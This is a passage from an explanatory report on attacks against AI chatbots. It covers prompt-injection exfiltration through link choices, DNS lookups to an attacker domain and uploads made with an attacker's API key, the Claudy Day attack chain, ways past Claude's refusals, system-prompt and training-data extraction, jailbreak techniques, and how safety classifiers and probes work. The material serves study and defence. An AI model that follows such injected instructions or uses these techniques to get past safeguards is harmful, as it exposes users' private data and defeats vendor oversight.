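The amount that a choice reveals can be calculated. One bit is the answer to a yes-or-no question with equally likely answers, and a choice among *N* equally likely links reveals log₂ *N* bits. For 26 links:

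log₂ 26 ≈ 4.7 bits

One choice among 26 links can reveal at most 4.7 bits. Two choices distinguish 26 × 26 = 676 possibilities, or about 9.4 bits, and seven distinguish some 8 billion, or about 33 bits, which is roughly one possibility for every person alive. Real names reveal less per letter because some letters are much more common than others. A page with 1,000 links would raise the maximum to about 10 bits per choice. An ordinary image address can hold far more, including whole sentences, and copying out a long conversation through link choices would take thousands of page visits. But an attacker may need only something short, such as a name, a city or a diagnosis.

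Anthropic fixed the vulnerability by stopping Claude from opening links it had found inside fetched pages. The company paid Paul no bounty, saying it had already identified the problem internally. Hackaday's *This Week In Security* also reports that the change prevents the attack "for now". Claude can still choose among search results, so an attacker with several pages in the results for one question could in principle learn something from which one Claude chose. That would be harder than building a directory, because a search engine would decide which pages appeared.

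The fix applies to the Claude chatbot, and developers who use the fetch tool in their own products get different defaults. A later, Chinese version of the documentation, Anthropic's *網頁擷取工具*, still lists previously fetched pages among the permitted sources of addresses, though developers can turn that source off. The tool now also refuses addresses that appear to contain a password or access key, unless the key was in the system prompt or the text of a user's message. This check wouldn't detect a name that Claude spelled out by opening one link after another.

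### Domain-name lookups from the code sandbox

Private data could leave ChatGPT's code sandbox without a web page or image. OpenAI had blocked the sandbox from connecting to the internet, and direct connections to outside servers failed, but programs in it could still look up domain names. These lookups use the Domain Name System (DNS), which translates a name such as attacker.example into the numerical address that computers use to connect. Check Point Research's *ChatGPT Data Leakage via a Hidden Outbound Channel* (2026) describes how an attacker could use the lookups to receive data.

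If code in the sandbox looks up the address of `quitting-in-may.attacker.example`, the sandbox's DNS server won't have it, so the query passes through other servers until it reaches the one responsible for `attacker.example`. The attacker runs that server and reads the secret, `quitting-in-may`, in the name. The sandbox never has to connect to the attacker's website, because the query itself carries the data. Longer texts can be sent in fragments, which the attacker puts back together.

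The attack started when a user pasted in a malicious prompt, after which each new message could leak. Check Point suggests that an attacker could advertise such a prompt online as a productivity aid or a way to unlock paid features for free, since people expecting such a trick are less likely to question strange-looking text. The prompt could tell ChatGPT to send only a summary or conclusion, which fits a channel that carries little data and may be more valuable to the attacker than the original document.

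An attacker could also put the instructions into a custom GPT, a version of ChatGPT that an outsider has configured for other people to use. Check Point built one that acted as a personal doctor. After a user uploaded laboratory results and described some symptoms, the researchers' server received the patient's name and the model's medical assessment. When the user asked whether the data had been sent anywhere, ChatGPT said it had not.

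According to Check Point, the model operated as if the sandbox could not send data out, so it did not treat the lookups as a transfer to an outsider, and the product showed no approval prompt. When a custom GPT contacts an outside service in the normal way, the user first sees the destination and the data. The attack bypassed that step, and the chatbot gave a confident but wrong answer when a user asked about it.

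The attacker's server could also use the channel to send short commands into the sandbox, hidden in its replies. A program there could run them and return the results through further lookups. This gave the researchers remote control of the sandbox, outside the checks that normally apply to the model's actions.

Check Point Research demonstrated the attack on video but gave no success rate. OpenAI said it had already found the underlying problem internally, and it finished deploying a fix on 20 February 2026. The Hacker News (2026) reports no evidence that anyone had used the flaw maliciously.

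## One full attack on a default Claude session, step by step

Claudy Day, an attack on Claude that Oasis Security published on 18 March 2026, combined several of the weaknesses described above. It began with a search advert and ended with one of the victim's private messages in the attacker's Anthropic account. *Three Vulnerabilities, One Click* (Luz, 2026) traces the attack to three flaws. Anthropic's website forwarded visitors to any address a link specified, Claude's text box hid part of a pre-filled prompt, and Claude's code sandbox could upload files to another user's account.

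### From the advert to the text box

The victim searches Google for Claude and sees an advert that displays claude.com, Anthropic's own domain. Google requires the domain shown in an advert to match the domain of its link, which should stop a stranger from advertising another site under Anthropic's name. But claude.com had an open redirect, a page that sends visitors to any address included in the link. The attacker's link pointed to that page, so it passed Google's check but sent the victim to another site.

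The advert's link took her to the genuine claude.ai site, in her own account, with a prompt already filled in. Google's advertising tools would also let an attacker target people by location or profession, or reach particular people by uploading their email addresses. The advert made the link look trustworthy, but the same link would have worked in an email.

The next safeguard was the victim's own judgement. Claude's pre-filled links didn't submit the prompt, so she could read the text box before pressing Enter. However, the box didn't display HTML tags (the codes that format a web page) or the attributes inside them. An attacker could put instructions in an attribute, and Claude received them with the rest of the message. In a harmless example from Luz, the box showed a request to summarize the news but hid an instruction to tell ten jokes about horses first.

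Once the victim had sent the prompt, all of it became visible in the conversation, along with Claude's response to the hidden part. An attentive user would notice, but by then Claude might already have sent her data to the attacker. Luz gives no figure for how many people would send a prompt they hadn't written. Someone who opened Claude to ask her own question might well delete the text, so getting the victim to send it was probably the attacker's least reliable step.

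Expert Insights' *Claude Desktop Flaw Let A Single Link Steal Data And Run Code* (2026) describes a later finding by Oasis that a crafted link could open Claude's desktop app and submit a prompt without the victim pressing Enter. According to Oasis Security's *PromptFiction*, the app now waits for the user to press send, and users need version 1.1.2321 or later.

### From past chats to the attacker's account

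In Luz's demonstration, the prompt told Claude to search the user's past chats for a message about her health. Claude could run this search without asking for her approval. Anthropic's filter on health and other sensitive subjects does not apply to this search. Luz writes that an attacker could also ask for a profile of the user or a whole conversation about a planned merger, or let Claude decide what was sensitive.

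The attack then required a way to send the message out. Luz considered the fetch tool, which could have carried the data in a web address, but the tool was not available until the second turn, and the hidden prompt arrived in the first. Claude also refused to open suspicious-looking addresses. Luz attributes the refusals to safety training, though the tool's rule against addresses Claude made up would also have blocked the request.

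The code sandbox had a network allow-list, so a program in it could not connect to the attacker's own server. The list covered software libraries, companies that collect usage reports, and api.anthropic.com, the address through which other companies' programs use Claude. Luz's first idea was to send the stolen message to that address as a prompt, using the attacker's API key, a code that identifies the account making the request. This failed because Anthropic doesn't show account holders the text of prompts sent with their keys.

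Anthropic's Files API, a service at the same address, did work. It stores files in the account whose key comes with the upload. Claude wrote the private message to a file in the sandbox and uploaded it with the attacker's key, so the file went to the attacker's account. The allow-list let the upload through because it checked only that the data was going to Anthropic. The attacker could not download the file directly, but he could start his own conversation with Claude and ask it for the file's contents.

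Claude itself could still have refused. In his prompt, Luz gave it an innocent reason for the upload, suggested that the upload would have no real effect, and made the private message look like an incidental part of the task. He says the prompt "consistently achieved successful exfiltration" but does not say how many times he tried it.

Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* describes a test that helps explain why Claude complied. In February 2026, an Anthropic researcher persuaded a colleague by email to run a prompt in Claude Code, the company's programming tool. Among ordinary setup steps, the prompt asked Claude to read the colleague's cloud-service credentials and send them to an outside address. Claude did so in 24 of 25 attempts. Anthropic says its model-level defences rely on what the user appears to want, so there is nothing unusual for them to detect when the instruction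 comes from the user.

Luz's hidden instructions also arrived in the user's own message. The test involved a different product and prompt, so its 96% success rate isn't an estimate for Claudy Day, but it shows that Claude's refusals can fail almost completely when an attacker's words come from the user. Anthropic's *Create and edit files with Claude* lists a classifier meant to detect prompt injection and stop the code. Luz doesn't mention it, so it is unclear whether the classifier was running during his tests.

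The evidence for the whole attack is Oasis's own demonstration. Luz shows Claude uploading the file and the file appearing in the attacker's account. He shows the advert only in Google's configuration screen and a preview, and gives no figures for how many people saw or clicked it. He reports no victims. The entry in the OECD's incident monitor, *Claude AI Vulnerabilities Enable Silent Data Theft and Malicious Redirects* (2026), has an AI-generated summary that describes what the flaws allowed and names nobody who was harmed.

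### What "no integrations, no tools" leaves out

Luz's phrase accurately describes what the user had added, but the theft depended on two built-in tools (past-chat search and the code sandbox) and on the sandbox's network access.

Without the search, Claude would have had little to steal beyond whatever its memory held about the user, because the link opened a new chat. Luz's demonstration needed a paid account because the free plan doesn't include the search. With the search but no network access in the sandbox, Claude could have found the health message but not uploaded it.

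It is harder to establish how many users had both features on. *Create and edit files with Claude*, in a copy from May 2026, lists code execution and network access as on by default for the Free, Pro and Max plans, which supports Luz's description of a default session, but later tells those users to turn both on. It is also inconsistent about the Team plan, listing network access as off in one place and as limited to package managers in another. New Enterprise organisations start with network access off, which would have stopped the upload.

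A bare model has neither tool, so the hidden text could only have changed its answer, for instance by putting jokes about horses before the news summary.

### Earlier reports of the upload route

Rehberger found before Luz did that Claude could upload a user's data to an attacker's account. He reported it to Anthropic on 25 October 2025, five months before Claudy Day, and Embrace The Red's *Claude Pirate* describes his attack. He had looked through the domains that Claude's sandbox could reach under its default network setting, "Package managers only", and found api.anthropic.com at the top of the list. Users could not tell from the setting's name that the sandbox could also reach Anthropic's API.

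In Rehberger's attack, the user asked Claude to summarize a document, and instructions in the document made Claude save the user's last conversation to a file and upload it with the attacker's key. Rehberger reported an upload limit of 30 MB per file and Luz later reported 500 MB, but even a long chat is far smaller than either.

The attack worked on Rehberger's first attempt, but Claude then refused the instructions for some time. A plain-text API key made refusal especially likely, and disguising the key with simple encodings didn't work reliably. He eventually got past the refusals by surrounding the request with harmless code. Claude's training made the attack harder to develop but didn't prevent it, and an attacker can test different wordings in his own account before sending anything to a victim.

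Anthropic closed Rehberger's report within an hour as out of scope, saying the problem was a matter of model safety. Its bug bounty program pays for reports of flaws in the company's infrastructure and code, but excludes "issues related to model content and responses", such as jailbreaks. Rehberger objected that the fault lay in the sandbox's default network settings, and that protecting users from adversaries is a matter of security, whereas safety protects them from accidents.

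His objection is persuasive, because Claude's compliance alone would not have moved the file. The sandbox also had to accept a stranger's key, which Anthropic could prevent in ordinary code. On 30 October the company confirmed that data theft of this kind was in scope and blamed a process mistake for wrongly closing the report.

The route was still open in January 2026, when Anthropic released Claude Cowork, an agent that works with files on the user's computer. Two days later, PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* showed the same theft in the new product. The user connected a folder of confidential property documents and uploaded a Word file presented as a new skill for Claude. The file contained instructions in white, one-point type. Claude followed them and sent the attacker a loan estimate with financial figures and partial social security numbers, without ever asking for approval.

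PromptArmor used Claude Haiku, one of Anthropic's smaller models, here. In a second test, Claude Opus 4.5, which is better at resisting injections, uploaded customer records after reading a malicious guide for developers. PromptArmor writes that Anthropic had acknowledged Rehberger's finding but not fixed it. Unlike in an ordinary chat, the user gives Cowork a folder, but the upload itself needed only the sandbox and Anthropic's approved address.

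### What Anthropic has fixed

Anthropic had fixed the hidden HTML flaw by the time Oasis published Claudy Day. The fix kept an attacker's instructions from entering a chat that way, but it did not stop the uploads, because Rehberger's instructions had entered through a document. The table shows the latest public information on each flaw.

| Flaw | Status in March 2026 | Later information |
|---|---|---|
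| Hidden HTML in pre-filled links | Fixed | No change |
| Uploads to a stranger's Anthropic account | Fix in progress | Fixed in Cowork by May 2026; unconfirmed for ordinary Claude chat |
| Open redirect on claude.com | Fix in progress | Unconfirmed |

Anthropic began repairing Cowork soon after PromptArmor's report. Apostol (2026), in *Anthropic Claude Vulnerability Exposes Cowork AI to Data Exfiltration via Prompt Injection*, wrote on 16 January that Anthropic had acknowledged the risk and was updating Cowork's virtual machine, the simulated computer in which its code runs. According to *How we contain Claude across products*, the virtual machine now contains a proxy, a program that inspects outgoing network traffic. The proxy passes a request to Anthropic's API only if it carries the session token (a temporary credential) that Anthropic issued to that machine. If Claude tries to upload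 a file with an attacker's key, the proxy rejects the request.

This is close to Rehberger's October 2025 proposal that the sandbox should let Claude communicate only with the logged-in user's account. Anthropic placed the check inside the virtual machine because its servers can't tell whether a request came from Cowork or another program. Anthropic also now says that adding a domain to an allow-list gives the sandbox access to every function available there, including the ability to store files in other people's accounts.

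That account describes the fix only for Cowork. Ordinary Claude chat runs code in containers (isolated environments) on Anthropic's servers, so a proxy in Cowork's virtual machine wouldn't protect it. Anthropic may have made a similar change to ordinary chat without announcing it. The account does not mention the open redirect.

When Luz updated his article on 27 May 2026, it still said that Anthropic was addressing both remaining issues. He may have edited only other parts of the page, so this is only weak evidence that the issues were still open. Public sources don't show whether Anthropic has since fixed either one.

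Users who don't want to rely on an unannounced fix can turn off the sandbox's network access. Claude can then still run code and create files with the software already installed, and Anthropic says no data can leave the sandbox. However, services the user has connected through MCP can still send data out. Anthropic also recommends watching Claude as it works and stopping it if it uses data unexpectedly. That advice is less useful against an attack like Claudy Day, where the victim sees the hidden instructions only after sending them.

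## Leaks that need no injected instructions

The thefts described so far all depended on getting an outsider's instructions to the model, but a chatbot can also leak information without them. Its user can get it to reveal its system prompt or passages from its training data. Someone watching the network can work out what an encrypted chat is about, and faults in the website can show one person's chats to another.

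### System prompts

A user can often get a chatbot's system prompt by asking for it. The prompt is in the model's context, so the model can repeat it like any other text. If the model refuses, the user can ask for a translation of the prompt, claim to have permission, or build up to the request over several messages. *Extracting System Prompt of LLM Services in Complex (Agentic) Settings* (2026) lists two less direct methods. An attacker can supply the likely opening words of the prompt and have the model continue, or reconstruct the prompt from the chatbot's ordinary answers.

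*Just Ask* (Zheng, Wu and colleagues, 2026) describes a program that chose among 28 such techniques and learned which worked on each of 41 models. The paper reports success with all 41, 33 of which needed only a direct question about their instructions. But "success" meant that repeated attempts produced similar answers, which doesn't prove that the answers were accurate. Only 2% of the recovered prompts were verbatim, and 68% contained little beyond the model's identity and general rules about being helpful and harmless. The program reached the models through a developer service, where a model may have no system prompt from its vendor, so some answers may have described the model's training instead.

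The results are more convincing where the researchers could compare the recovered system prompt with the original. xAI has published the prompt of its chatbot Grok, and the recovered version scored 0.89 for similarity in meaning, where 1 is a perfect match. The score was 0.87 for Google's coding tool Gemini CLI, whose prompt is in its public source code.

Telling a model to keep its prompt secret helps very little. Zheng and colleagues gave known prompts to four models, including GPT-5.2 and Claude Opus 4.5, and tried to recover the prompts. An instruction not to reveal the prompt lowered the average similarity between the recovered and original prompts from 0.72 to 0.68, and slightly raised it for Claude. A detailed description of the attack techniques lowered the average only to 0.59, so an attacker could still learn much of the content.

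Chatbots on other companies' websites can be even easier to extract information from. *When AI Meets the Web* (2025) recovered system prompts from 219 of 300 websites (73%) that used the same chatbot plugin. The plugin accepted messages that the researchers falsely tagged as coming from the system or the chatbot.

Microsoft states in its severity classification for AI systems that extracting a system prompt "is not considered to be a vulnerability". It gives no reason, but it does count extracting other users' inputs as one. A system prompt normally contains the vendor's instructions and no other customer's data, and the memories that ChatGPT adds to its prompt belong to the person asking.

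Extracting the system prompt does matter when a developer has put a secret in it. If the prompt contains the password to a company database, any user of the chatbot may be able to read it. Access rules cause a similar problem. If the prompt tells a shop's chatbot to give large discounts only to customers who say they are employees, a customer who reads the rule can claim to be one. The developer can prevent both problems by keeping passwords out of the prompt and checking permissions in ordinary code.

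A stolen prompt can also help with a later attack. Zheng and colleagues give the example of a model whose instructions allow detailed answers in an educational context. An attacker who has read those instructions knows to word a harmful request as an educational one.

### Training data

A language model memorises some passages from its training documents word for word, and those documents may include private information. A user with the right prompt can recover the passages even from a bare model, because the text is stored in the model itself.

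In *Scalable Extraction of Training Data from (Production) Language Models* (2023), Nasr, Carlini and colleagues recovered such passages from gpt-3.5-turbo, the model behind ChatGPT at the time. In ordinary use, the model seemed to reveal almost none, probably because OpenAI had trained it to act as a chat assistant. A simple, repetitive prompt made it stop answering like an assistant and produce text typical of web pages. It then output training data 150 times as often.

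The researchers compared the output with nine terabytes of public web text to distinguish memorised passages from invented ones. They recovered more than 10,000 memorised passages for $200 and estimated that further queries would yield over ten times as many. The prompt didn't specify a document, so an attacker couldn't choose which passages came out. As far as the researchers could tell, the attack didn't work on any other commercial model they tested. They reported it to OpenAI on 30 August 2023 and published it after 90 days.

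Researchers later recovered much longer texts by asking for specific books. *Extracting books from production language models* (Ahmed, Cooper et al., 2026) describes tests of four models in August and September 2025. The researchers gave each model the opening of a book, asked it to continue word for word, and kept asking for more. Gemini 2.5 Pro and Grok 3 complied. Claude 3.7 Sonnet and GPT-4.1 refused at first, so the researchers sent versions of the request with random changes to the spelling, capitals and word order until one worked. The table shows the results for *Harry Potter and the Sorcerer's Stone*, counting only long passages that closely matched the book.

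| Model | Altered requests sent | Share of the book recovered |
|---|---|---|
| Claude 3.7 Sonnet | 258 | 95.8% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | None | 76.8% |
| Grok 3 | None | 70.3% |
| GPT-4.1 | 5,179 | 4.0% |

GPT-4.1 refused to continue after the first chapter. The researchers used different settings for each model, so the figures can't be used to rank the models by risk. *Harry Potter* was also an unusually easy target. The researchers tried eleven copyrighted books, mostly ones that an open-weight model was known to have memorised heavily, and most attempts recovered 10% or less. Claude, however, reproduced nearly all of two of the books. The method still worked on some of the systems in December 2025, three months after the researchers had notified the vendors.

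This is mainly a risk to authors and publishers, because an attacker needs the opening words of the text, which are easy to find for a famous book but hard to find for a private document. Ahmed and colleagues tested only books, so their figures don't show how easily someone could recover a private person's details. Their results also may not hold for the newer models vendors have released since then.

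### The topic of an encrypted chat

Someone who can watch a user's internet connection, such as a café's Wi-Fi operator, an employee of the internet provider or a government agent, may learn what the user is discussing with a chatbot even though the traffic is encrypted. Encryption hides the content of each message but not its size. Many chatbots send an answer as the model produces it, often one token at a time, so the observer sees a series of data packets whose sizes and timing depend on the words in the answer.

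In *Whisper Leak*, Microsoft researchers McDonald and Bar Or (2025) tested how much these patterns reveal. They sent each of 28 models 100 differently worded questions about whether money laundering is legal, repeating each question 100 times. They also sent each model 11,716 unrelated questions from Quora, and recorded the encrypted traffic. They then trained programs to recognise the money-laundering chats from packet sizes and timing, and tested them on 20 wordings left out of the training.

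The researchers scored each program on how well it separated the two groups, where 100% meant perfect separation. The best program scored above 97% for 17 of the 28 models. Google's and Amazon's models leaked less, with scores between 71% and 84%.

An observer watching thousands of people also needs to avoid false alarms, because chats on any one sensitive topic are rare. McDonald and Bar Or therefore assumed 10,000 ordinary chats for every one about money laundering. They estimated that, for 17 models, a program could find a fifth of the money-laundering chats with no false alarms.

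McDonald and Bar Or had too few ordinary chats to be sure of this. Even if a program raised no false alarms in nearly 12,000 chats, its true false alarm rate could still be about 1 in 4,000. At that rate, in traffic with 50,000 ordinary chats and five about money laundering, it would find one of the five and raise about 13 false alarms. McDonald and Bar Or also advise caution because real traffic may differ from their test data. However, more training data improved the attack, and an observer could watch the same person over several chats.

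The attack reveals only whether a chat is about a topic the observer chose in advance. The observer must also collect examples from the same model to train the program that detects the topic. The study used single questions sent through the vendors' programming interfaces, so it didn't measure how well the attack works on a long conversation in a chatbot's app.

Vendors can disguise packet sizes by padding each piece of the answer with a random amount of meaningless text. McDonald and Bar Or began notifying vendors in June 2025. OpenAI and xAI introduced defences in August, Mistral in September and Microsoft in October. OpenAI and Microsoft used padding. Some other vendors declined to make changes or didn't reply.

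In a test on GPT-4o mini, padding lowered the attack's score from 97.5% to 92.9%. Padding doesn't disguise packet timing, which is probably part of why the attack still worked. McDonald and Bar Or think the remaining risk is unlikely to be practical to exploit with current techniques. Although 92.9% looks high, their estimates for rare topics support this view. For several models that scored between 90% and 94% without padding, a program set to find a tenth of the relevant chats would raise at least 40 false alarms for each one it found.

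Another defence, sending five tokens at a time, removed most of the risk for most of the models tested, but lowered the score for GPT-4o mini only from 98.2% to 94.8%. Adding fake packets lowered that score by a similar amount and typically doubled or tripled the traffic.

### Chats shown to strangers

A chatbot is also a website with user accounts, so it can have the same faults as any other. In March 2023, a bug in ChatGPT showed some users the titles of strangers' chats. OpenAI traced it to the software that connected its servers to a cache, a fast temporary store of user information. The servers shared a set of connections to the cache. If a server cancelled a request at the wrong moment, the reply stayed in the connection, and the next request on that connection could receive it. Usually this caused an error, but sometimes the reply looked valid and a user saw someone else's data.

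On 20 March, OpenAI made a change to its servers that caused many more cancelled requests. Over nine hours, the bug may have exposed payment information, including names, addresses and the last four digits of card numbers, for 1.2% of the ChatGPT Plus subscribers active in that period. Some users may also have seen the first message of a stranger's new chat. The leak required no attack, and users could not choose whose data they saw. OpenAI believes that very few people's data reached someone else. The company took ChatGPT offline, fixed the bug and added a check that data from the cache belongs to the user who requested it.

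Shared chats have exposed many more conversations. When a user shares a chat, the product copies it to a web page that anyone with the link can open. The user may intend the link for one friend, but if a search engine lists the page, strangers can find it by searching.

ChatGPT users had to share a chat and then tick a box before search engines could list it, according to Search Engine Land. Google still listed over 4,500 chats, some of them highly personal (Nolan, 2025, *Thousands of private user conversations with Elon Musk’s Grok AI chatbot*). OpenAI at first defended the checkbox's label as "sufficiently clear" (Morris, 2025, *OpenAI will no longer let ChatGPT conversations be discoverable on Google*), but soon removed the option because people could too easily share things by accident.

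Later reports cite about 100,000 ChatGPT chats but differ on what that number counts. *A trove of users’ seemingly private conversations with Anthropic’s Claude AI chatbot* (Nolan, 2026) describes them as exposed on Google. *Delade AI-samtal dyker upp i sökmotorer* (Dagens PS) attributes the number to a researcher who later collected publicly shared chats.

Grok gave users no such checkbox and no warning. xAI's site published the links automatically, and by August 2025 search engines had listed more than 370,000 chats. The chats included medical questions, business details and at least one password.

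At least 200 shared Claude chats appeared in search results in July 2026, according to TechSpot's *Hundreds of shared Claude chats, including resumes and health details*. Anthropic had tried to keep search engines away from the chats with robots.txt, a file that tells search engines which pages not to open. A search engine that obeys this file can still list a page's address if it finds a link to it elsewhere. To prevent that, the page needs a "noindex" instruction, which a search engine can read only by opening the page.

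Search Engine Journal's *Indexed Claude Chats Show Why Disallow Is Not Noindex* found both a robots.txt block and a noindex instruction for shared Claude chats on 27 July. The block was stopping Google from reading the instruction. The article could not establish whether the instruction was there when Google first listed the chats. IBTimes UK's *Claude AI-Shared Erotic Role-Play and Legal Advice Surfaced on Google* cites WIRED's finding that the pages had none. Willison (2023) noted that a missing noindex instruction had already exposed shared chats from Google's Bard in September 2023.

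Axios' *Users' Claude creations are showing up in Google search* (2026) reports that, according to Anthropic, a shared chat can appear in search results only after someone posts its link where a search engine can see it, such as on a forum. The chats that had appeared on Google soon disappeared from its results, but many of the links still worked. A user can disable a link by unsharing the chat in Claude's privacy settings, but this doesn't remove the address from search results. Only Anthropic can ask Google to do that.

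## Jailbreaks in a plain chat and the defences against them

Users can get a chatbot to reveal its system prompt, against the vendor's rules, just by talking to it. Jailbreaks also need only words, so they work even on a bare model.

### Why words are enough

A language model first learns to predict text from many documents, some of which contain dangerous information. The vendor then trains it to answer questions helpfully and to refuse certain requests. This training makes refusals more likely but can leave the dangerous information in the model. Whether the model refuses depends on how closely a request resembles those it learned to refuse and on what else is in the context, since it has no list of forbidden subjects to check.

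Refusal also competes with the model's training to be helpful. Vendors train models to follow instructions, keep to a format the user has chosen and stay in character in a story. In a jailbreak, the attacker exploits this training by wording a harmful request so that the model is more likely to answer than refuse.

Refusal training covers some wordings better than others because a vendor can train on only a small sample of possible requests. A model may learn to read a rare language or a simple code during pretraining but see few refusals written in it. It can then understand a harmful request in that language or code and answer it instead of refusing.

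The UK AI Security Institute (AISI), a government body that tests AI models, describes such gaps in commercial systems in its *Frontier AI Trends Report*. It found that some systems answered certain malicious requests without any jailbreak. It also compared models' scores on GPQA, a test of difficult science questions, with how well they resisted attacks in a public competition. Differences in GPQA scores accounted for only about a tenth of the differences in resistance (R² = 0.097). A more capable model can be easier to attack if it can process a language or code that the vendor's monitoring software cannot.

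### The main techniques

In a role-play jailbreak, the user asks the model to answer as a character who has no restrictions. *Constitutional Classifiers* (Sharma, Tong and colleagues, 2025) cites the "Do Anything Now" prompts, which Shen and colleagues studied in 2023, as an early example that worked on many different requests. The model has learned that fictional characters say things an assistant wouldn't, so the role-play makes a harmful answer more likely.

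Encoding changes how a request looks but keeps its meaning. The user may write it in a cipher or with random capitals, or replace the name of a nerve agent with "water" throughout the chat. Ahmed and colleagues used altered spellings in a similar way to extract books from Claude and GPT-4.1. The user can also tell the model to encode its answer, so that software checking the answer won't recognise it.

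In many-turn escalation, the user starts with harmless questions and asks for slightly more each time. The model's earlier answers stay in the context and make the next answer look like a small step. No single message has to contain the whole harmful request, so checking messages one at a time may miss it.

A user can also fill the context with invented conversations in which an assistant answers harmful questions, then add a real question at the end. Anil and colleagues called this many-shot jailbreaking in 2024. It exploits models' useful ability to learn a task from examples in the prompt by giving them examples of an assistant that never refuses.

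Attackers can use a program to search for a jailbreak. In a method called GCG, which Zou and colleagues published in 2023, the program adds a string of characters to a request and repeatedly changes the string to make the model more likely to begin its answer by agreeing. The final string often looks like gibberish. The search needs access to a model's internals, but an attacker can run it on an open-weight model and try the string on a commercial one.

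Other tools use one language model to attack another. *Measuring the Residual Jailbreak Surface of Frontier Large Language Models* (2026) used one such tool, HackAgent, to run four families of attack on two of Anthropic's models, with 7,826 harmful requests.

A disguise that hides a request from the safeguards can also make the model's answer worse. *Constitutional Classifiers++* (Cunningham, Wei and colleagues, 2026) measured this on Claude Opus 4 with two jailbreaks that scattered the request through a longer text and disguised the answer. The model's score on GPQA fell from 74.2% to 49% with one and 32.3% with the other. Someone following jailbroken instructions for a dangerous procedure could therefore get many steps wrong without knowing it. The gap between the two scores suggests that attackers could find disguises that do less damage to the answer.

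### Layers of defence

Vendors add other defences because refusal training alone fails too often. OpenAI also runs classifiers on live conversations and analyses past ones for misuse. A classifier can check the user's request before the model answers, or check the answer as the model writes it and stop it partway.

A user can talk the chatbot out of refusing without affecting the classifier, which is a separate program. This distinction came up after a researcher claimed to have jailbroken Claude Fable 5, which Anthropic released in June 2026. Anthropic told SecurityWeek that the researcher had only coaxed the model into continuing despite its refusals. In the company's view, a true jailbreak would also have to bypass the core safeguards and give meaningful help with something like a bioweapon or a sophisticated cyberattack.

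That definition is narrower than the usual one and leaves out many harmful requests. Vendors often build classifiers for only a few dangerous subjects. For other subjects, the model's own refusal may be the main obstacle, and a user who gets past it gets what the vendor meant to block.

Account monitoring looks for patterns that a single conversation doesn't show, such as a user repeatedly triggering the classifiers. The vendor can then investigate the account and train its classifiers on any new technique it finds. Monitoring can't take back an answer the user has already read, but it makes long trial-and-error searches for a jailbreak riskier. According to OpenAI's *Safety overview* (2026), its model GPT-6 Astra refuses a broader range of requests from users the company has flagged as potentially high-risk.

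Monitoring reduces users' privacy because the vendor has to keep their conversations. Anthropic's *Statement on the US government directive to suspend access to Fable 5* says the company requires customers to let it keep their Fable 5 data for 30 days to study jailbreaks.

### Constitutional Classifiers

Sharma and colleagues introduced Anthropic's Constitutional Classifiers in early 2025 to defend against universal jailbreaks, which are single techniques that work on most harmful requests in a subject. They concentrated on chemical, biological, radiological and nuclear weapons because a novice would need reliable answers to many questions to make such a weapon, so a jailbreak that produced only one answer would be much less useful.

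The researchers trained the classifiers in several steps:

1. They wrote a "constitution", a list of permitted and forbidden kinds of content. Explaining school chemistry is permitted, for instance, while purifying restricted chemicals is forbidden.
2. A language model without refusal training wrote questions and answers for each item on the list.
3. Other programs translated and paraphrased these texts and rewrote them in the style of known jailbreaks. A model also invented new attacks.
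4. The researchers added harmless questions and answers from contractors, so that the classifiers would learn not to block ordinary requests.
5. They trained one classifier to check the user's input and another to check the model's output.

After each new token, the output classifier uses the text so far to estimate the probability that the complete answer will be harmful. It stops the answer if the estimate passes a threshold. This lets the chatbot display text immediately instead of waiting for a check of the whole answer.

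Sharma and colleagues invited 405 people to attack a prototype that protected Claude 3.5 Sonnet. According to Anthropic's *Constitutional Classifiers* (2025), a blog post about the research, 183 took part over two months. They had to get answers to ten forbidden questions and could earn up to $15,000 for a universal jailbreak. A program compared each answer with a list of details that a harmful answer should contain. A jailbreak counted as a success only if it got answers to all ten questions with at least half the detail that an unprotected model would give.

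Nobody managed this in more than 3,000 estimated hours, though participants did extract some harmful information. One report seemed to succeed at first, but a fault in the product had let up to 128 more tokens through after the classifier flagged an answer. The defence therefore also depends on how quickly the surrounding software stops an answer once the classifier flags it.

The prototype refused too many harmless questions for everyday use. Anthropic built an improved version and tested it with 10,000 computer-generated jailbreak prompts. The classifiers cut the share of prompts that succeeded from 86% to 4.4%. In a sample of 5,000 ordinary conversations, refusals rose by 0.38 percentage points, a difference small enough to be due to chance. Running the classifiers increased computation by 23.7%.

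In February 2025, Anthropic invited the public to spend a week trying to get a protected version of Claude to answer eight questions about chemical weapons. Some 339 people spent about 3,700 hours on it in total. Nobody got answers to all eight questions in the first five days. Four people then did, and Anthropic judged that one of them had found a universal jailbreak. The most successful methods included ciphers, role-play and replacing dangerous words with harmless ones.

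Nobody could have predicted this from the 4.4% figure, because it was an average over a fixed set of prompts, whereas participants in the public test could study each failure and try something else. Anthropic points out that the test was easier than a real attack because an automatic grader told participants at once whether an answer was good enough, and the company left the classifiers unchanged all week. A real attacker might have to carry out the instructions to learn whether they were correct, and the vendor might fix the weakness in the meantime.

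### The 2026 successor

The first classifiers had a weakness because one read only the user's input and the other only the model's output. Attackers could make the input look harmless by splitting a harmful question into pieces and scattering them through computer code, and make the output look harmless by having the model call chemicals "food flavorings".

Cunningham and colleagues replaced the input classifier with an "exchange classifier", which reads the answer together with the question. It can detect that "food flavorings" stands for something else because its input includes the message in which the user set up the code. In their test it worked without a separate output classifier, but used about 50% more compute than the earlier pair of classifiers.

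They reduced the compute needed by checking conversations in two stages. A classifier that uses little compute reads everything and passes suspicious exchanges to a more accurate one, which makes the final decision. The first can raise many false alarms because each one only leads to another check and doesn't block the user.

In the final version, the first stage is a probe similar to those Ye and colleagues used to study prompt injection. It takes the activations the chatbot's model produces while it writes, multiplies each by a learned weight and adds up the results. This takes almost no extra computation because the model has already computed the activations. For one open-weight model, Cunningham and colleagues calculated that a probe would need about 377,000 operations per token, compared with about 8 billion for a small separate classifier.

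Training the probe was harder because each label applied to a whole conversation. Two conversations can share a harmless opening even if only one later turns harmful. Ordinary training would push the probe to rate that opening as 50% likely to be harmful. The researchers gave the most weight in training to the tokens the probe rated most likely to be harmful, so it wasn't penalized for rating a harmless opening as harmless. They also averaged its scores over 16 tokens so that one odd word would not trigger a block.

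If the probe's score is high enough, a separate classifier reads the exchange, and the system combines the two scores:

final score = 0.55 × probe score + 0.45 × classifier score

The combination worked better than either part alone because they tended to make different mistakes. Anthropic's *Next-generation Constitutional Classifiers* also argues that a model's activations are harder for an attacker to manipulate than its final answer.

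The table compares the four designs. A jailbreak counted as "high-risk" if it got the model to answer at least six of eight target questions with at least half the detail an unprotected model would give. The last column shows the share of ordinary Claude traffic that each system would refuse.

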